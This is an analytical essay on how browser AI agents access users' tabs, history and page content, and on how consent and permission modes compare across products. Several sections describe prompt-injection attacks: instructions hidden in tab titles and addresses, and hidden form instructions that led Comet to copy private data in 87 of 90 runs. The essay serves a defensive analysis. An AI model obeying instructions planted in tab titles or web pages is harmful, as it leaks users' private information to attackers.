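Cookies can't carry over a half-filled form. Google's *Connect your AI agent to your personal browser with auto-connect* similarly advises developers to connect the agent to the live session when someone has already reached a certain point, such as a late step in a complex checkout, and wants the agent to continue from there. It also warns that the agent then has access to all the data in the profile, including open tabs, cookies and stored data.

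A separate browser limits which accounts an agent can reach only if the user doesn't sign in to them there. BrowserOS's *Browser for AI agents* promotes neo as a second browser for the user's agents, signed in to the user's own accounts, including their bank. This separates the tabs, so the agent can't disturb a form in the user's everyday browser, but it can reach as many accounts as before.

Users may also return to the live session because it is convenient. OpenClaw's *Browser profiles* recommends the managed profile by default and two alternatives for tasks that need existing logins. It suggests the debugging connection if the user is at the computer to approve Chrome's prompt, and the extension, which doesn't need that prompt, if the user is away. With a new automatic pairing in "All tabs" mode, the agent would have access to nearly every open tab while nobody was watching.

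In the expense example, the agent could do most of the work with much less access. The user could sign in only to webmail in a separate browser profile, then have the agent find the invoice there and report the total. The user would have to type one number into the form, but the agent would have no access to the form or the bank account.

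## What can the agent see of tabs it has not been given?

An agent that is allowed to act only in its own tabs may still need to know what else the user has open. If the user asks it to put the invoice total in "the expense form I have open", the agent has to work out which tab that is before it can ask to use it. Some products solve this with metadata-only access, which lets the agent see details such as a tab's title and address but not the page's content.

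### What a tab listing contains

BrowserOS neo shows the agent the tabs' titles and addresses, which BrowserOS describes as context. Codex's more detailed listing covers the tabs in all the user's windows, with the most recently used first. Each entry has an identifier and can include the tab's title, its address, the time the user last opened or focused it, and the name of its tab group. The model uses this information to choose which tab to claim.

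These details come from SkillsMP's third-party copy of Codex's instructions. OpenAI's own page about the extension doesn't describe the listing. The user report *Chrome extension browser bridge can lose session ownership while tabs remain visible* mentions two commands, `getUserTabs` and `claimUserTab`, that closely match the copy, so the copy is probably right about the basic design.

Codex may list open tabs even when the task doesn't involve them. According to SkillsMP's copy, the model should test the connection on its first Chrome task with a simple call, "such as listing open tabs". The copy doesn't specify whether these are the agent's tabs or the user's. If they are the user's, a request to look up a train time would send the model the titles of any open mail or bank pages. OpenAI says it stores browser activity that becomes part of Codex's context, including tool calls, so those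 titles could remain in the stored conversation.

As of March 2026, Claude in Chrome appeared to give its model a tab list that covered only the session's tab group, according to sshh12. The extension could read the titles of tabs outside the group, but its harness didn't pass them to the model.

### The older rule for browser extensions

Browsers treated titles and addresses as sensitive before AI agents existed. Any Chrome extension can list the open tabs and see which tab is active, whether a tab is playing sound and when the user last switched to it. According to Google's *browser.tabs*, an extension can read a tab's title, icon, address and any address the tab is about to load only if it has the "tabs" permission or permission for the page's website.

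This rule protects the user's privacy but not their work. An extension without either permission can still reload a tab or load another address in it. It could replace the half-filled expense form even though it can't read "Expense claim" in the tab's title.

WebKit, the browser engine in Apple's Safari, also hides titles and addresses from extensions that lack permission. Hatcher (2023) proposed in *Some APIs like tabs.query need to prompt for permission before returning* that WebKit ask the user for the missing permission before answering the extension's request. Developers added the change in March 2024. The user now decides at the time an extension requests the information, whereas Chrome warns users mainly at installation.

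The rule does little to restrain AI extensions, because they ask for broad permissions. Codex's access to "all your data on all websites" covers the titles and addresses of ordinary web pages. Claude's extension requests the "tabs" permission, which Anthropic says lets Claude open, close and switch between tabs. According to Google, however, most tab features, including opening a tab, need no permission. The "tabs" permission adds the ability to read the four sensitive facts.

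### What titles and addresses reveal

Suppose the user's bank tab shows a page about a debt they are repaying. The table gives an invented entry for that tab, with the same kinds of facts as Codex's listing, and compares it with Chrome's older rule.

| Fact | Invented value | Can a Chrome extension read it without a permission? |
|---|---|---|
| Identifier | 13 | Yes |
| Title | Missed payment on your debt plan | No |
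| Address | `https://harbourbank.example/debt-plan/missed-payment` | No |
| Last opened | Today, 02:14 | Yes |
| Group name | Divorce | The tab's record contains only the group's number |

Even though the agent hasn't read the page, this information reveals that the user is in debt, has missed a payment and was looking at the problem in the middle of the night. The group name suggests a reason. A title such as "Your HIV test result is ready" would also reveal medical information.

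This information could affect what the agent does elsewhere, as the user's union membership did in the AgentTell experiment. That experiment used page content, not titles, but a title can contain the same kind of fact. If the expense form has a box for urgent reimbursement, an agent that knows about the missed payment might tick it and so reveal to the employer something the user had kept private.

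The agent can also copy an address from the listing, open it in a signed-in tab of its own and read the page. Metadata-only access therefore protects a page only if something else, such as a site permission, stops the agent from opening the same address. Some addresses don't require a sign-in. For example, a private link to a shared document may contain a secret code that lets anyone with the link read the document.

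A harness could reveal less by searching the tab titles itself. If the user mentions an expense form, the harness could return only tabs that match "expense" and keep the bank tab out of the model's input. The search would sometimes fail, for instance if the form were titled "Untitled", and the agent would then have to ask the user which tab they meant.

### Instructions hidden in a title

Websites choose their own titles and addresses, so a listing also gives the model text written by strangers. A malicious page that the user opened and forgot about could have an instruction in its title, and the agent would receive it without visiting the page. If the user's webmail puts the subject of the open message in the tab's title, anyone who emails the user could write part of the listing.

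Anthropic found attacks of this kind when it tested its extension. *Piloting Claude in Chrome* (2025) says attackers can hide instructions in tab titles and address text, where only an agent is likely to notice them. New defenses reduced the success rate from 35.7% to 0% on a set of four browser-specific attack types, but Anthropic gives no separate figure for titles and addresses. In its broader tests of 123 cases, defenses reduced the rate from 23.6% to 11.2%. Anthropic could therefore stop the particular attacks in the smaller set, but tab titles may still be unsafe to read.

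### Browsing history

Codex can also search the user's browsing history. Each result contains an address, the time of the visit and usually a title, much like an entry in the tab listing. But history goes back further and can include visits from other devices where the user is signed in to Chrome. OpenAI warns that the history may contain internal company addresses and search terms, and that a malicious page could increase the risk of Codex copying them somewhere the user didn't intend.

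As of June 2026, Codex asks for approval every time before it uses the history, and the user has no option to allow it permanently. The user can, however, permanently approve a website or turn off website prompts altogether.

How much a single approval reveals depends on the search. In SkillsMP's copy, the model can specify a search term, a range of dates and a maximum number of results, but all of these are optional. A search for "invoice" over the past week would probably return a few harmless pages, while one with no limits could return much of the user's recent browsing. The user would need to see the search to make a sensible decision about approving it, but OpenAI doesn't specify whether the prompt shows it.

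OpenAI documents no similar prompt for the tab listing, even though the listing can overlap heavily with browsing history. For someone who keeps sixty tabs open for weeks, it is a partial history that includes when they last visited each page. One argument for treating the listing more leniently is that the agent needs some kind of list to find the tab the user is talking about. Another is that users can see their open tabs and close the private ones before starting a task, which is much harder with months of history. Neither argument justifies collecting the list for tasks that don't involve the user's tabs.

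ChatGPT's Mac app has a separate feature, Computer History, which helps it recall earlier work in apps and on websites. According to OpenAI's *Using your computer and browser*, the feature is off by default, and the user chooses which apps and websites to include. This consent is broader than approving one history search, because it also covers pages the user hasn't visited yet.

### The tab in front of the user

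An agent in a side panel often receives the content of the page beside it, not just the title. Claude captures the active tab when its side panel opens, so Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* advises users not to open the panel while viewing sensitive information. Opening the panel therefore serves as permission to see the page, even if the user only wanted to ask about something else.

Chrome's older "activeTab" permission works similarly. It gives an extension temporary access to the current tab when the user invokes the extension, and it triggers no warning at installation. But the extension doesn't have to use this access immediately. A side panel could wait until the user asks a question about the page. Firefox's AI Mode worked much like this in early 2026, according to Roesner and Kohlbrenner. The agent received the page's text only when the user clicked "Summarize page", and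 the user could see the text in the chat.

Anthropic can store what Claude captures. As of December 2026, it saves side panel sessions to the user's history, and the user can reopen them on other devices. When Claude works in its "Automatically approve" mode, an automated safety check can also see the latest screenshot, and Anthropic can keep a copy in its record of the check. If a user briefly opens the panel on their bank page, their balance may be saved in both the session history and that record.

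ChatGPT's extension also opens beside the current page, and an update on 30 July 2026 let it compare several open tabs. For TechRadar's *I gave ChatGPT access to my mess of open Chrome tabs*, the reviewer opened a weather forecast, a museum, a restaurant and a hiking guide, and asked ChatGPT to use all the open tabs to plan a Saturday afternoon. The plan accounted for the expected showers and the museum's opening hours, so ChatGPT had evidently used the pages' content as well as their titles. The reviewer had asked for this, but a user could easily say "all of my open tabs" without remembering that a bank page was open, and the request would include that page too.

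### Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests

Roesner and Kohlbrenner ran the broadest comparison of what these agents read in early 2026. They used the latest stable version of each product on a Mac, and built web pages that each named a different animal that a fictional Alice likes. The main page mentioned cats, a page embedded in it mentioned horses, and a page in another tab mentioned koalas. If the agent answered "cats and koalas", it had read both tabs.

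If an agent read something even once, the researchers recorded that it could. If it failed or refused, they tried at least three more times in new chats. They also typed text into an ordinary field and a password field and asked the agent what the fields contained.

| Agent | Tabs from another origin | Embedded pages from another origin | Text the user typed | Masked password |
|---|---|---|---|---|
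| Brave Leo | With the user's permission | No | No | No |
| Atlas, ordinary mode | Only through chat memory | No | Yes | No |
| Atlas, Agent Mode | No | Yes | Yes, in its logged-in setting | Yes, in its logged-in setting |
| Chrome with Gemini | With the user's permission | Yes | Yes | No |
| Claude for Chrome | With the user's permission | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Edge with Copilot | Yes | No | No | No |
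| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No | No |
| Comet | No, only from the same origin | Yes | Yes | No |

Copilot was the only agent that freely read tabs from other origins. Brave, Gemini and Claude read another tab only after the user had added it to the request. The test question explicitly asked about "both open tabs", so the result doesn't show that Copilot looked at other tabs unprompted.

Limits on reading other tabs didn't guarantee limits within a page. Claude needed permission to read another tab, but once it had access to a page, it also read embedded pages from other origins and a password that the screen showed only as dots. Copilot read other tabs freely but didn't read embedded pages at all. Embedded pages, also called frames, often contain advertisements or other companies' services, so a user who gives an agent access to one tab may be giving it content from several websites.

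All the agents could read parts of the main page that the user had scrolled past, so scrolling the balance on the bank page out of sight would not have protected it. Claude and both modes of Atlas also read text that the page's code kept invisible. Anthropic's warning about what is visible on the screen therefore understates what Claude could read at the time.

An agent could also retain what it read on a page after losing access to it. Near the end of the tests, the researchers asked Comet what animals Alice liked, and it listed seven from earlier chats and pages. A false statement can persist in the same way. Roesner and Kohlbrenner give the example of a phishing page with a fake phone number for the user's bank. The agent might recognize the page as fraudulent at first, but later repeat the number after losing track of where it came from.

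#### What the results can't show

The tests recorded what the agents did, which isn't always everything they could do. An agent may fail to read a frame because the browser never passes it on, or because the model declines to use it. Only the first is firm protection, since a better-worded request or an attack might get the model to use a frame it has received.

Firefox was the clearest case, because the researchers could see the exact text it sent to the model, and that text left out embedded pages (frames). Copilot consistently answered that it saw no sign of frames, which suggests a similar design but doesn't prove it. Atlas in its ordinary mode sometimes included frames in early trials and later stopped, so the restriction may have come from the model. The "Yes" results are more certain than the "No" results, though one success doesn't show how often an agent would succeed.

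In a later experiment, published in June 2026, Wang and colleagues put a page with private information in a frame on another website's page, then asked BrowserOS to summarize the whole page and write the summary in a text box there. BrowserOS copied the private information into the box in every run, with all three models they tried and without any attack. The request arguably invited this, since the embedded page was part of what the user saw, but a user who asks for a summary may not realize that part of the page comes from another website. When the two pages were separate and the agent visited them in turn, the researchers saw no such leaks unless they added an attack.

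#### Responses and changes since

The researchers gave the vendors more than 60 days' notice. Google, Microsoft and Brave sent replies that the researchers considered thoughtful. OpenAI declined the report because it didn't include a complete prompt injection attack. The University of Washington, where both researchers work, later reported that Perplexity had also declined it and that Anthropic and Firefox hadn't responded.

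In the paper, Roesner and Kohlbrenner recommend that users avoid agentic browsers until the security improves. In their FAQ of 15 April 2026, they advise only caution, but they specifically warn against Claude for Chrome because, as an extension, it can run its own code in web pages. Microsoft, whose browser they placed on the safer side, partly funded the work through gifts.

Atlas, the only product on which the researchers completed a data theft, is no longer available. OpenAI moved its agent to the ChatGPT desktop app and the Chrome extension, which the study didn't cover, so the Atlas results don't show what the extension reads. The Chrome extension's broad permissions resemble those of Claude's extension, but in SkillsMP's copy, Codex's model doesn't have the usual command for running its own code in a page.

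Since the study, Claude in Chrome has become less protective in some ways and more protective in another. At the time, Anthropic blocked banking sites completely, and the extension didn't appear to save its chats to the user's account. As of December 2026, Anthropic lets Claude use financial sites with the user's permission and saves the side panel's sessions. Claude can also connect to the password manager 1Password, which fills in logins without showing Claude the password. That should help with the masked-password problem, but only for passwords that 1Password enters. Anthropic doesn't specify whether Claude can still read a password that the user types.

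Roesner and Kohlbrenner found that Comet met the conditions for cross-site data theft, but they didn't find a prompt injection that worked on it. Wang and colleagues found one in June. They had Comet handle private information on one test page and then visit a form containing hidden instructions from an attacker. Comet copied the information into the form in 87 of 90 runs across three models. It didn't need access to the first tab by then, because the information was still in its conversation.

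## When should the agent ask before acting on a tab the user already has open?

An agent can avoid asking about most of the user's tabs by opening the same page, such as a webmail inbox, in a tab of its own. It needs permission to use the user's tab only when that tab holds something a new copy would lack, such as entries in a half-filled expense form.

### State that exists only in the tab

Pages without forms can also hold state that a new tab may lack. Google suggests connecting an agent to the live session when a developer has reproduced an error by hand, since the error might not appear in a new tab. Google's *Let your Coding Agent debug your browser session with Chrome DevTools MCP* (2025) adds that a developer can select a failing network request in Chrome's tools and have the agent investigate it. Some websites also store sign-in data in session storage, which belongs to a single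 tab, so a new tab on the same site may start signed out.

The agent can't always tell from a listing whether a tab holds anything of this kind. Chrome's record of a tab, which Google documents for extension developers, includes whether the page has recently played sound and whether Chrome has discarded it from memory, but not whether it has unsaved entries. Sound is a useful warning because the user may be on a call, as in the second Adom incident. A discarded tab reloads when the user returns to it, so working there usually has little advantage over opening a new copy.

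The agent can often find out whether it needs the user's tab by opening the same address in its own tab. If the user's entries appear there, the site has saved them and the agent can read them without using the user's tab. Typing in the new tab is riskier, because it may overwrite a draft the user is still editing in the original. If the new tab is empty, the agent needs the user's tab. This test is unsafe for addresses that do something when opened, such as a one-time confirmation link.

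If the agent only has to read a page, the user can also send it the content once. OpenClaw's 2026.8.1 release let users send a page or selected text to the main conversation without giving the agent continuing access to the tab. By December, OpenClaw had dropped page sharing from its extension.

### Ways to hand over a tab

When the agent does need a user tab, products differ in who starts the handover and how much it covers.

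| Method | Who starts it | What the agent receives | How long access lasts and how it ends |
|---|---|---|---|
| Naming the tab in a request (BrowserOS neo, undated) | The user | Permission to work on the tab the user describes | BrowserOS doesn't specify |
| Sharing chosen tabs (OpenClaw's "Selected tabs" mode, December 2026) | The user, by moving a tab into the group | Reading and control of that tab | Until the user moves the tab out, pauses it or disconnects the extension |
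| Dragging a tab into the agent's group (Claude in Chrome, December 2026) | The user | Viewing and acting on the tab, along with the others in the group | Anthropic doesn't specify |
| Claiming a listed tab (Codex, undated copy) | The agent | Commands to click, type, navigate, reload and close | Until the cleanup at the end of the turn, unless the model keeps the tab |
| Auto-connect (Chrome, December 2025) | The agent's tool asks for a connection, and the user clicks "Allow" | Every tab in the profile, with its cookies and stored data | Until the connection ends, after which a new one needs a new approval |

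Naming a tab takes the least effort from the user. BrowserOS's examples are asking the agent to reply to the email the user is reading or to extract numbers from the document on the screen. The drawback is that the model has to work out which tab the user means and judge when the permission has run out, for instance if the user's next request is about something else.

Moving a tab into a group identifies which tab the user means, but it doesn't limit what the agent may do there. A user who shares the expense form so the agent can type one number also enables the agent to reload the form. Claude users don't need to drag the first tab into a group, because Claude already works "on the tab in front of you", according to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome*.

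A tab picker lets the agent ask for a tab when it needs one and lets the user choose which. *Playwright MCP Chrome Extension*, Glama's copy of the instructions for a Microsoft tool that connects agents to Chrome, describes a page that opens when the model first uses the browser, where the user selects the tab to connect. Users can also set up a token to skip approving each connection, but they then lose a chance to notice a mistake.

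Chrome's auto-connect gives the agent access to far more than most requests need. In one of Google's sample prompts, the user asks about a dashboard "open in the next tab", but clicking "Allow" also gives the agent access to a bank page open in another tab. During the session, Chrome shows a banner saying that automated test software is controlling it, but the banner doesn't show which tab the agent is using.

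The user's approval in the dialog also applies to a connection rather than a task. *fix(connect): single consenting WebSocket*, a code change to one tool, describes a bug in which the tool opened a brief test connection before the real one. The user's click approved only the test, so Chrome requested approval again for the real connection, and the user saw repeated prompts or a command that hung. But a tool that keeps one connection open all day could carry out many unrelated tasks after a single click.

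### Why claiming a tab isn't consent

In Codex, the agent itself takes control of the user's tab. According to SkillsMP's copy of the instructions, it does this by passing an entry from the tab listing to the `claimTab` command.

Claiming an open tab lets the harness add it to the record of what the agent may use. This record shows that the agent has control of the tab, but not whether the user agreed to that. The user may have asked for it, may have approved the website for another purpose, or may not know about it. A harness that requires consent therefore has to record it separately, specifying the tab, the permitted actions and when permission ends.

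A site permission doesn't settle which tab the agent should act on. Suppose the user has two half-filled claims open, one for March and one for April. A single approval of the website in OpenAI's prompt covers both tabs. If their titles are identical, the model may choose the tab the user looked at last, which could be the wrong one. SkillsMP's copy also includes an instruction not to ask a clarifying question just because a request that mentions @chrome is ambiguous. This instruction is probably about which browser to use, but a model could easily apply it to the choice of tab.

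OpenAI's store listings don't mention a separate prompt for claiming a tab either. In the May 2026 Chrome Web Store listing, OpenAI promised that Codex would ask before accessing sites, referring to browsing history, and uploading or downloading files. In the same extension's listing as of 2 December, titled *ChatGPT*, OpenAI mentions prompts only for history and file transfers, and advertises that ChatGPT can act "in your tabs". A store listing needn't mention every safeguard, so the shorter list doesn't show that OpenAI removed the site prompt.

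### How browsers already tie permission to a tab

Browsers had to solve a similar problem for ordinary extensions. Chrome's activeTab permission takes effect only after the user deliberately invokes the extension. According to Google, the user can do this by clicking the extension's button, choosing its item in a menu, pressing its keyboard shortcut or accepting its suggestion in the address bar. The extension can then see the tab's title and address and, if it also has permission to run scripts, read and change the page.

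Access ends when the user closes the tab or goes to a different origin. Since Chrome 72, it has continued when the user moves between pages of the same origin. These limits are meant to reduce the harm a compromised extension can do. An attacker has to wait until the user invokes the extension, and then can access only that tab.

Under the same rule, a user could click the browser agent's button on the expense form, and the agent could work in that tab until the tab left the expense system. If the agent loaded the webmail there by mistake, the form would still be lost, but the agent would immediately lose access to the tab.

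The short life of the activeTab permission can also be a nuisance. When Level Access, which makes software for testing web accessibility, first investigated using activeTab in its own extension, users who looked something up in another tab lost the connection and had to restart the tool. Google says access ends when the user navigates away or closes the tab, not when they switch tabs, so the tool itself may have caused part of the trouble. But an agent that worked across several websites in one tab would lose access whenever it moved to a new origin. An agent with its own tabs mostly avoids this because it can, for example, find an invoice there and use the user's tab only to fill in a form.

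The user's gesture also has to grant access to the right tab. In *activeTab permission not granted for tab on which the contextmenu is used*, robwu reported that when a Firefox user right-clicked a background tab and chose an extension's menu item, the extension received access to the tab in front instead. Developers fixed this in Firefox 63. The same bug in a browser agent could give it access to a bank page when the user had chosen the tab with an expense form.

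Firefox has temporary permissions that apply in a single tab, such as for access to the user's location or camera. According to Mozilla's *Browser-Scoped Permissions*, an approval covers one origin, while a refusal covers the whole site, including its subdomains. If the user lets `https://maps.example.com` use their location, `https://shop.example.com` still has to ask. If the user refuses the maps page, the shop page can't ask in that tab either. Otherwise, a site could keep asking from one subdomain after another.

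Firefox never writes permissions for a single tab to disk. It deletes them when the tab closes, or earlier if they have a timer. Within that tab, they also override the saved setting for the website. Site permissions for agents lack such an override. With one, a user who always allows the agent on an expense system could still keep it out of a tab with a half-filled form.

In Firefox, a refusal applies in only one tab, so an agent could respond by asking for the next tab on the same site. For agents, a refusal should instead cover all the user's tabs on that site until the task ends. It shouldn't cover the agent's own tabs, because then keeping the agent out of a form at `expenses.company.example` would also stop it from finding the invoice at `mail.company.example`.

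### Ending access

OpenClaw describes no rule that limits the agent to one website in a tab shared in "Selected tabs" mode. If the user shares the tab with the expense form and later opens their bank in it, the agent apparently keeps its access. Sharing also continues after a dropped connection, because OpenClaw restores the tabs that are still shared. The user can also cut off access by canceling Chrome's debugging session, which OpenClaw doesn't restart automatically.

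A better default would be to end access when the task finishes or the tab goes to another origin, whichever comes first. Someone who shares a tab to have one number entered may forget to drag it out of the group afterward. Some tasks need longer access, such as watching a dashboard all afternoon, but the user can choose that explicitly.

Users also need to be able to see what access they have granted. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* describes a settings page where users can see which websites they have chosen to always allow, revoke those permissions and review their permission history. The guide doesn't describe a similar list for tabs. A tab group that controls access partly serves as one, since the user can see at a glance which tabs are in it.

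Withdrawing access stops later actions, but the model keeps what it has already read, and any text it has typed stays in the page. If the user withdraws access while the agent is filling in a form, the harness should report which fields the agent changed. It shouldn't clear them, because that would mean acting in a tab it no longer has permission to use.

### Which actions need a question

The table proposes a rule for each kind of action, reasoned from what that action can disclose or destroy. It does not describe any vendor's policy.

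| Action in a user tab | Alternative to try first | The request is enough if | Ask first if |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading | Open the page in an agent tab | The user identified the tab and asked about its content | The agent only suspects that the tab is relevant |
| Typing | Fill in a new copy, if the user's entries don't matter | The user identified the form and what to enter, and the field is empty | The field already contains something, or the page may send text as the agent types |
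| Navigating | Open the new address in an agent tab | The user asked for this tab to change, and it holds nothing unsaved | The tab may hold unsaved entries, a call or a reply that is still arriving |
| Reloading | Open a fresh copy in an agent tab | The user asked to reload this tab, and it holds nothing unsaved | The agent wants to reload for its own reasons, or might erase something |
| Closing | Leave the tab open | The user specified which tabs to close, and they hold nothing unsaved | The agent chose the tabs, or one may hold unsaved entries |
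| Submitting | Leave the page ready for the user to submit | The user asked for submission and knows what the agent will send | The user asked only for the form to be filled in, or the content has changed since they agreed |

Reading a tab can do harm even though it leaves the page unchanged, because the user can't take back what the model has learned. The agent should rarely need to ask before navigating or reloading a user's tab, because it should rarely do either. It can easily open another tab instead.

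Closing tabs is a harder case because users may want help with it. OpenAI's December listing for the ChatGPT extension includes organizing and cleaning up tabs among its uses. A user who asks for this has agreed to have some tabs closed but hasn't decided which ones. The agent could list the tabs it proposes to close, leaving out any that might contain unsaved work, and ask for approval once instead of asking about each tab.

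Submitting the expense claim needs its own decision even when the agent uses a tab it opened, because the claim reaches the employer either way. With the alternative in the table, the user only has to press a button and can check the total first.

A harness can enforce some of these rules much more easily than others. In SkillsMP's copy of Codex's interface, loading an address, going back, reloading and closing a tab are separate commands, so code could block each one in a user tab. Submitting has no separate command because it may happen through a click or by pressing Enter, and a "Next" button in a long form may send data and change the page in one step. The harness could pause the page's network requests until the user approves, since programs connected through OpenClaw's extension can already pause requests, but many pages send requests constantly, and the harness would have to recognize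 which one submits the data.

Current lists of actions that need the user's approval don't clearly cover damage to an open tab. Anthropic promises on its product page that the agent will wait for the user before making purchases or doing "anything you can't undo." Its permissions guide requires explicit permission for permanent deletions, such as emptying the trash or deleting emails, files or messages. Reloading a page can also permanently erase what the user has typed into a form, but the guide doesn't mention this.

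### What the prompt should name

For the expense form, a useful prompt might be: "Enter 84.20 in the empty Total field of the March claim you have open? Nothing else will change, and the claim will not be submitted." The user can check this against the page in a few seconds. If the agent only asks to use `expenses.company.example`, the user doesn't know which tab it will change, what number it will enter or whether it will submit the claim.

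The prompt should show the website's address as the browser reports it, because the page controls its own title and could use it to mislead the user. If two tabs look alike, the harness can offer to bring the right one to the front. The prompt should also name the account. OpenAI advises users to check which account is active before they let ChatGPT continue, which matters to anyone signed in to both a personal and a work mailbox.

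If an action could erase something, the agent should tell the user what when it asks for permission. "Reload this page?" sounds routine, while "Reload this page and lose the three rows you added?" gives the user a reason to refuse. If the agent doesn't know exactly what the user would lose, it should at least warn that the form may contain unsaved entries.

Approval should also apply only to the tab and page that the prompt described. If the user agrees and then loads another page in the tab before the agent acts, the harness should cancel the action and ask again.

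### Whether a clear request is already consent

When a user writes "put the invoice total in the expense form I have open", there is a strong case for treating the request as consent. The user has already chosen the tab and the action, so a prompt that repeats them only adds a delay. Needless prompts may also teach users to approve without reading.

Codex's instructions follow this reasoning for some actions. In SkillsMP's copy of them, the agent can take one category of action if the user explicitly permitted it in the initial prompt. A second category always requires confirmation immediately before the action, and for a third, the agent must let the user take over or find another way. The copy doesn't list the actions in each category, so it's unclear how Codex treats claiming a tab. Claude also relies on the user's request. According to AI Toolbox's *Claude for Chrome* (2026), since 26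 August an automatic safety check has compared each action with the original request and blocked those that don't match.

The main argument for a separate prompt is that the user writes the request before knowing what the agent will find. They may have forgotten that a second claim is open, or that the Total field already contains a figure they worked out by hand. The model also interprets the request, so it determines whether its own access is already permitted. This is risky if the model misunderstands the request, and riskier if a malicious email has influenced it.

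These arguments apply to different requests, so a product can have the agent ask before some and not others. The agent can act without asking if the request identifies a single tab and the action, and the action can't destroy anything the user hasn't mentioned. The harness can check part of this without relying on the model, for example by confirming that only one open tab is on the expense system and that the field to be filled is empty. If either check fails, the agent should ask once, when it needs the tab, rather than before every keystroke.

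Under this rule, the agent could complete the expense example without a tab prompt. It would find the invoice in its own tab, type the total into the empty field and leave the claim for the user to submit. If the March and April claims were both open, it would ask only which one to use.

The user may not be there to answer, for instance if they are directing the agent from a phone, as OpenClaw's earlier documentation notes. They can avoid this problem by sharing just the expense form before leaving, without giving the agent access to every tab. If the user has shared nothing and doesn't reply, the agent can still find the invoice and report its total without changing the form.

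## How do the permission modes on offer compare?

Most current products ask the user about individual actions, websites, or a short list of sensitive steps such as payments, and few ask about a particular tab. The permission mode determines which prompts the user sees, so the same task can produce twelve prompts in one mode and none in another.

### Claude in Chrome

As of December 2026, a menu by Claude's chat box offers three modes. In "Manually approve", which Anthropic used to call "Ask before acting", the user approves Claude's actions. In "Automatically approve", an automatic review checks each action instead and blocks any that seem unsafe, such as an attempt to send the user's data to an attacker. After a block, Claude looks for a safer route or asks the user. After repeated blocks, it goes back to asking before every step. "Skip all approvals", formerly "Act without asking", removes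 the prompts and the automatic review. Anthropic recommends it only to users who completely trust everything involved in the task.

Manual approval works differently in the two versions of the side panel. In the older "classic" panel, Claude first writes a plan naming the websites it will use and its approach. The user can approve the plan or ask for changes. Claude then works alone within the plan, but asks before it uses another website or takes a sensitive step, such as downloading a file. For the expense task, the plan might name the webmail and the expense system. If it also included submitting the claim, the user could object before Claude acted.

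The newer panel runs as a session of Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, and has no plan. Claude may ask a question or two, then starts work and requests approval before each action. The user can allow that one action, allow all actions on the website, or refuse. This gives the user closer control of each step but less idea of what the later steps will be. A user who tires of approving single actions can only approve the whole site or change modes.

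The newer panel also starts in "Automatically approve", so many users will probably never see the manual prompts. If a user switches modes, the panel remembers their choice. Anthropic later announced, in an October update to *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), that automatic approval would also become the default for new sessions in most Claude apps on its Pro, Max and Team plans.

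Some limits apply in every mode. Claude needs explicit permission to change permission settings, grant authorizations, enter potentially sensitive information or permanently delete something. Anthropic prohibits it from making purchases or other financial transactions, creating accounts, handling sensitive card or identity data, downloading files from untrusted sources, giving investment advice, trading, modifying system files, and following instructions in emails or web content. Claude also asks before opening financial sites and can't open adult or known piracy sites, according to Anthropic's *Using Claude in Chrome safely*.

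These rules change, and they don't always agree with Anthropic's other statements. Anthropic prohibited permanent deletions outright in an earlier copy of the permissions guide, but Claude can now make them with permission. The guide still prohibits purchases, while on its product page Anthropic promises only that Claude will wait for the user before making one. A user therefore can't tell whether Claude would buy a train ticket if they approved it.

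The rule about instructions in emails is also hard to take literally. If a manager has emailed directions for filling in the expense form, the user may well want Claude to follow them. Anthropic presumably means instructions that the user hasn't asked Claude to follow.

### Does skipping approvals skip all of them?

Anthropic's guide is inconsistent about "Skip all approvals". It says Claude won't pause to ask in this mode, but it also lists sensitive actions that require explicit permission in every mode. These statements conflict when, for example, Claude is about to enter the user's home address in a form.

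Anthropic doesn't explain which rule takes precedence. ziyunli's *From Piloting Claude for Chrome* reproduces part of Anthropic's 2025 announcement of the extension's pilot, which described an experimental "autonomous mode" that kept certain safeguards for highly sensitive actions. If the current mode works the same way, Claude should still ask before entering the address. But the announcement didn't specify the safeguards, and the product has changed a great deal since, so it is safer to assume that Claude might not ask.

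Claude asks before downloading a file in manual mode, and on websites that the user has chosen to always allow. But downloads aren't on the list of actions that need permission in every mode. In automatic mode, Claude can apparently download a file from a trusted source without asking.

### Permission by website

OpenAI's Chrome extension mainly prompts the user for permission to use particular websites. The user can approve or decline each one, for one chat or permanently. As of June 2026, Codex could use sites on an allowlist without asking again and was not supposed to use sites on a blocklist. Removing a site from either list brought the prompt back.

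A setting named "always allow browser content" turned off all website prompts, and OpenAI labeled it an elevated risk. OpenAI doesn't specify whether the blocklist still applies when this setting is on, so users who have blocked their bank can't be sure the agent will stay off its site. OpenAI also says that the prompts cover hosts and the lists contain domains. If a company runs its mail and expense systems under one domain, the user can't be sure whether an entry for `company.example` covers both.

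Microsoft's agent for its Edge browser adjusts its prompts to how familiar a site is. Microsoft's *Browse with Copilot*, an undated help page, describes three levels:

- **Strict:** Copilot asks before working on any site.
- **Balanced:** Copilot works on popular, commonly trusted sites without asking, and asks about less common ones. Microsoft recommends this level.
- **Light:** Copilot works on most sites without asking.

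When Copilot asks for permission, the user can allow the site permanently or allow a single action. Edge also has an allow list and a block list. Microsoft states that Copilot can't use a site outside the allow list until the user approves it, but that description matches only the Strict level.

The Balanced level may help against obscure sites built to attack agents, but it suits the expense task badly. It would ask for permission on the employer's expense system, which is obscure but probably harmless, and not on the webmail, which is popular but lets strangers send instructions to the agent. Microsoft partly makes up for this by having Copilot ask the user to watch or take over on higher-risk sites such as email and banking.

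Edge also suspends an approved website's permission to use the camera, microphone or location while Copilot clicks, scrolls or types there. If Copilot only opens the site, the site keeps any of these permissions the user has given it.

Comet may ask the user for permission to carry out a whole task, according to The Hans India's undated report *Perplexity’s Comet Assistant Gets Major Upgrade With More Transparency, Control and Safety*. The user can do the task alone, let Comet act once, or give it ongoing permission. Perplexity's *Managing Comet Assistant permissions* adds that an organization's administrators decide whether the "Always Allow" option is available and whether Comet can control the browser at all.

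An allowlist can loosen or tighten these controls, depending on who sets it. When a Codex user adds a site to the allowlist, Codex asks less often and can still ask to use other sites. When an employer sets an allowlist for Claude, Claude can use only the sites on it, and the employer's blocklist overrides any permission the employee has given. Google's *Gemini in Chrome* names similar administrator policies for auto browse, but Google did not yet offer the feature to managed users.

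### Confirmations for sensitive actions

In Google's design for auto browse, software rather than the user decides whether most websites are relevant to the task. The user confirms only certain steps. Parker described three kinds of confirmation in December 2025.

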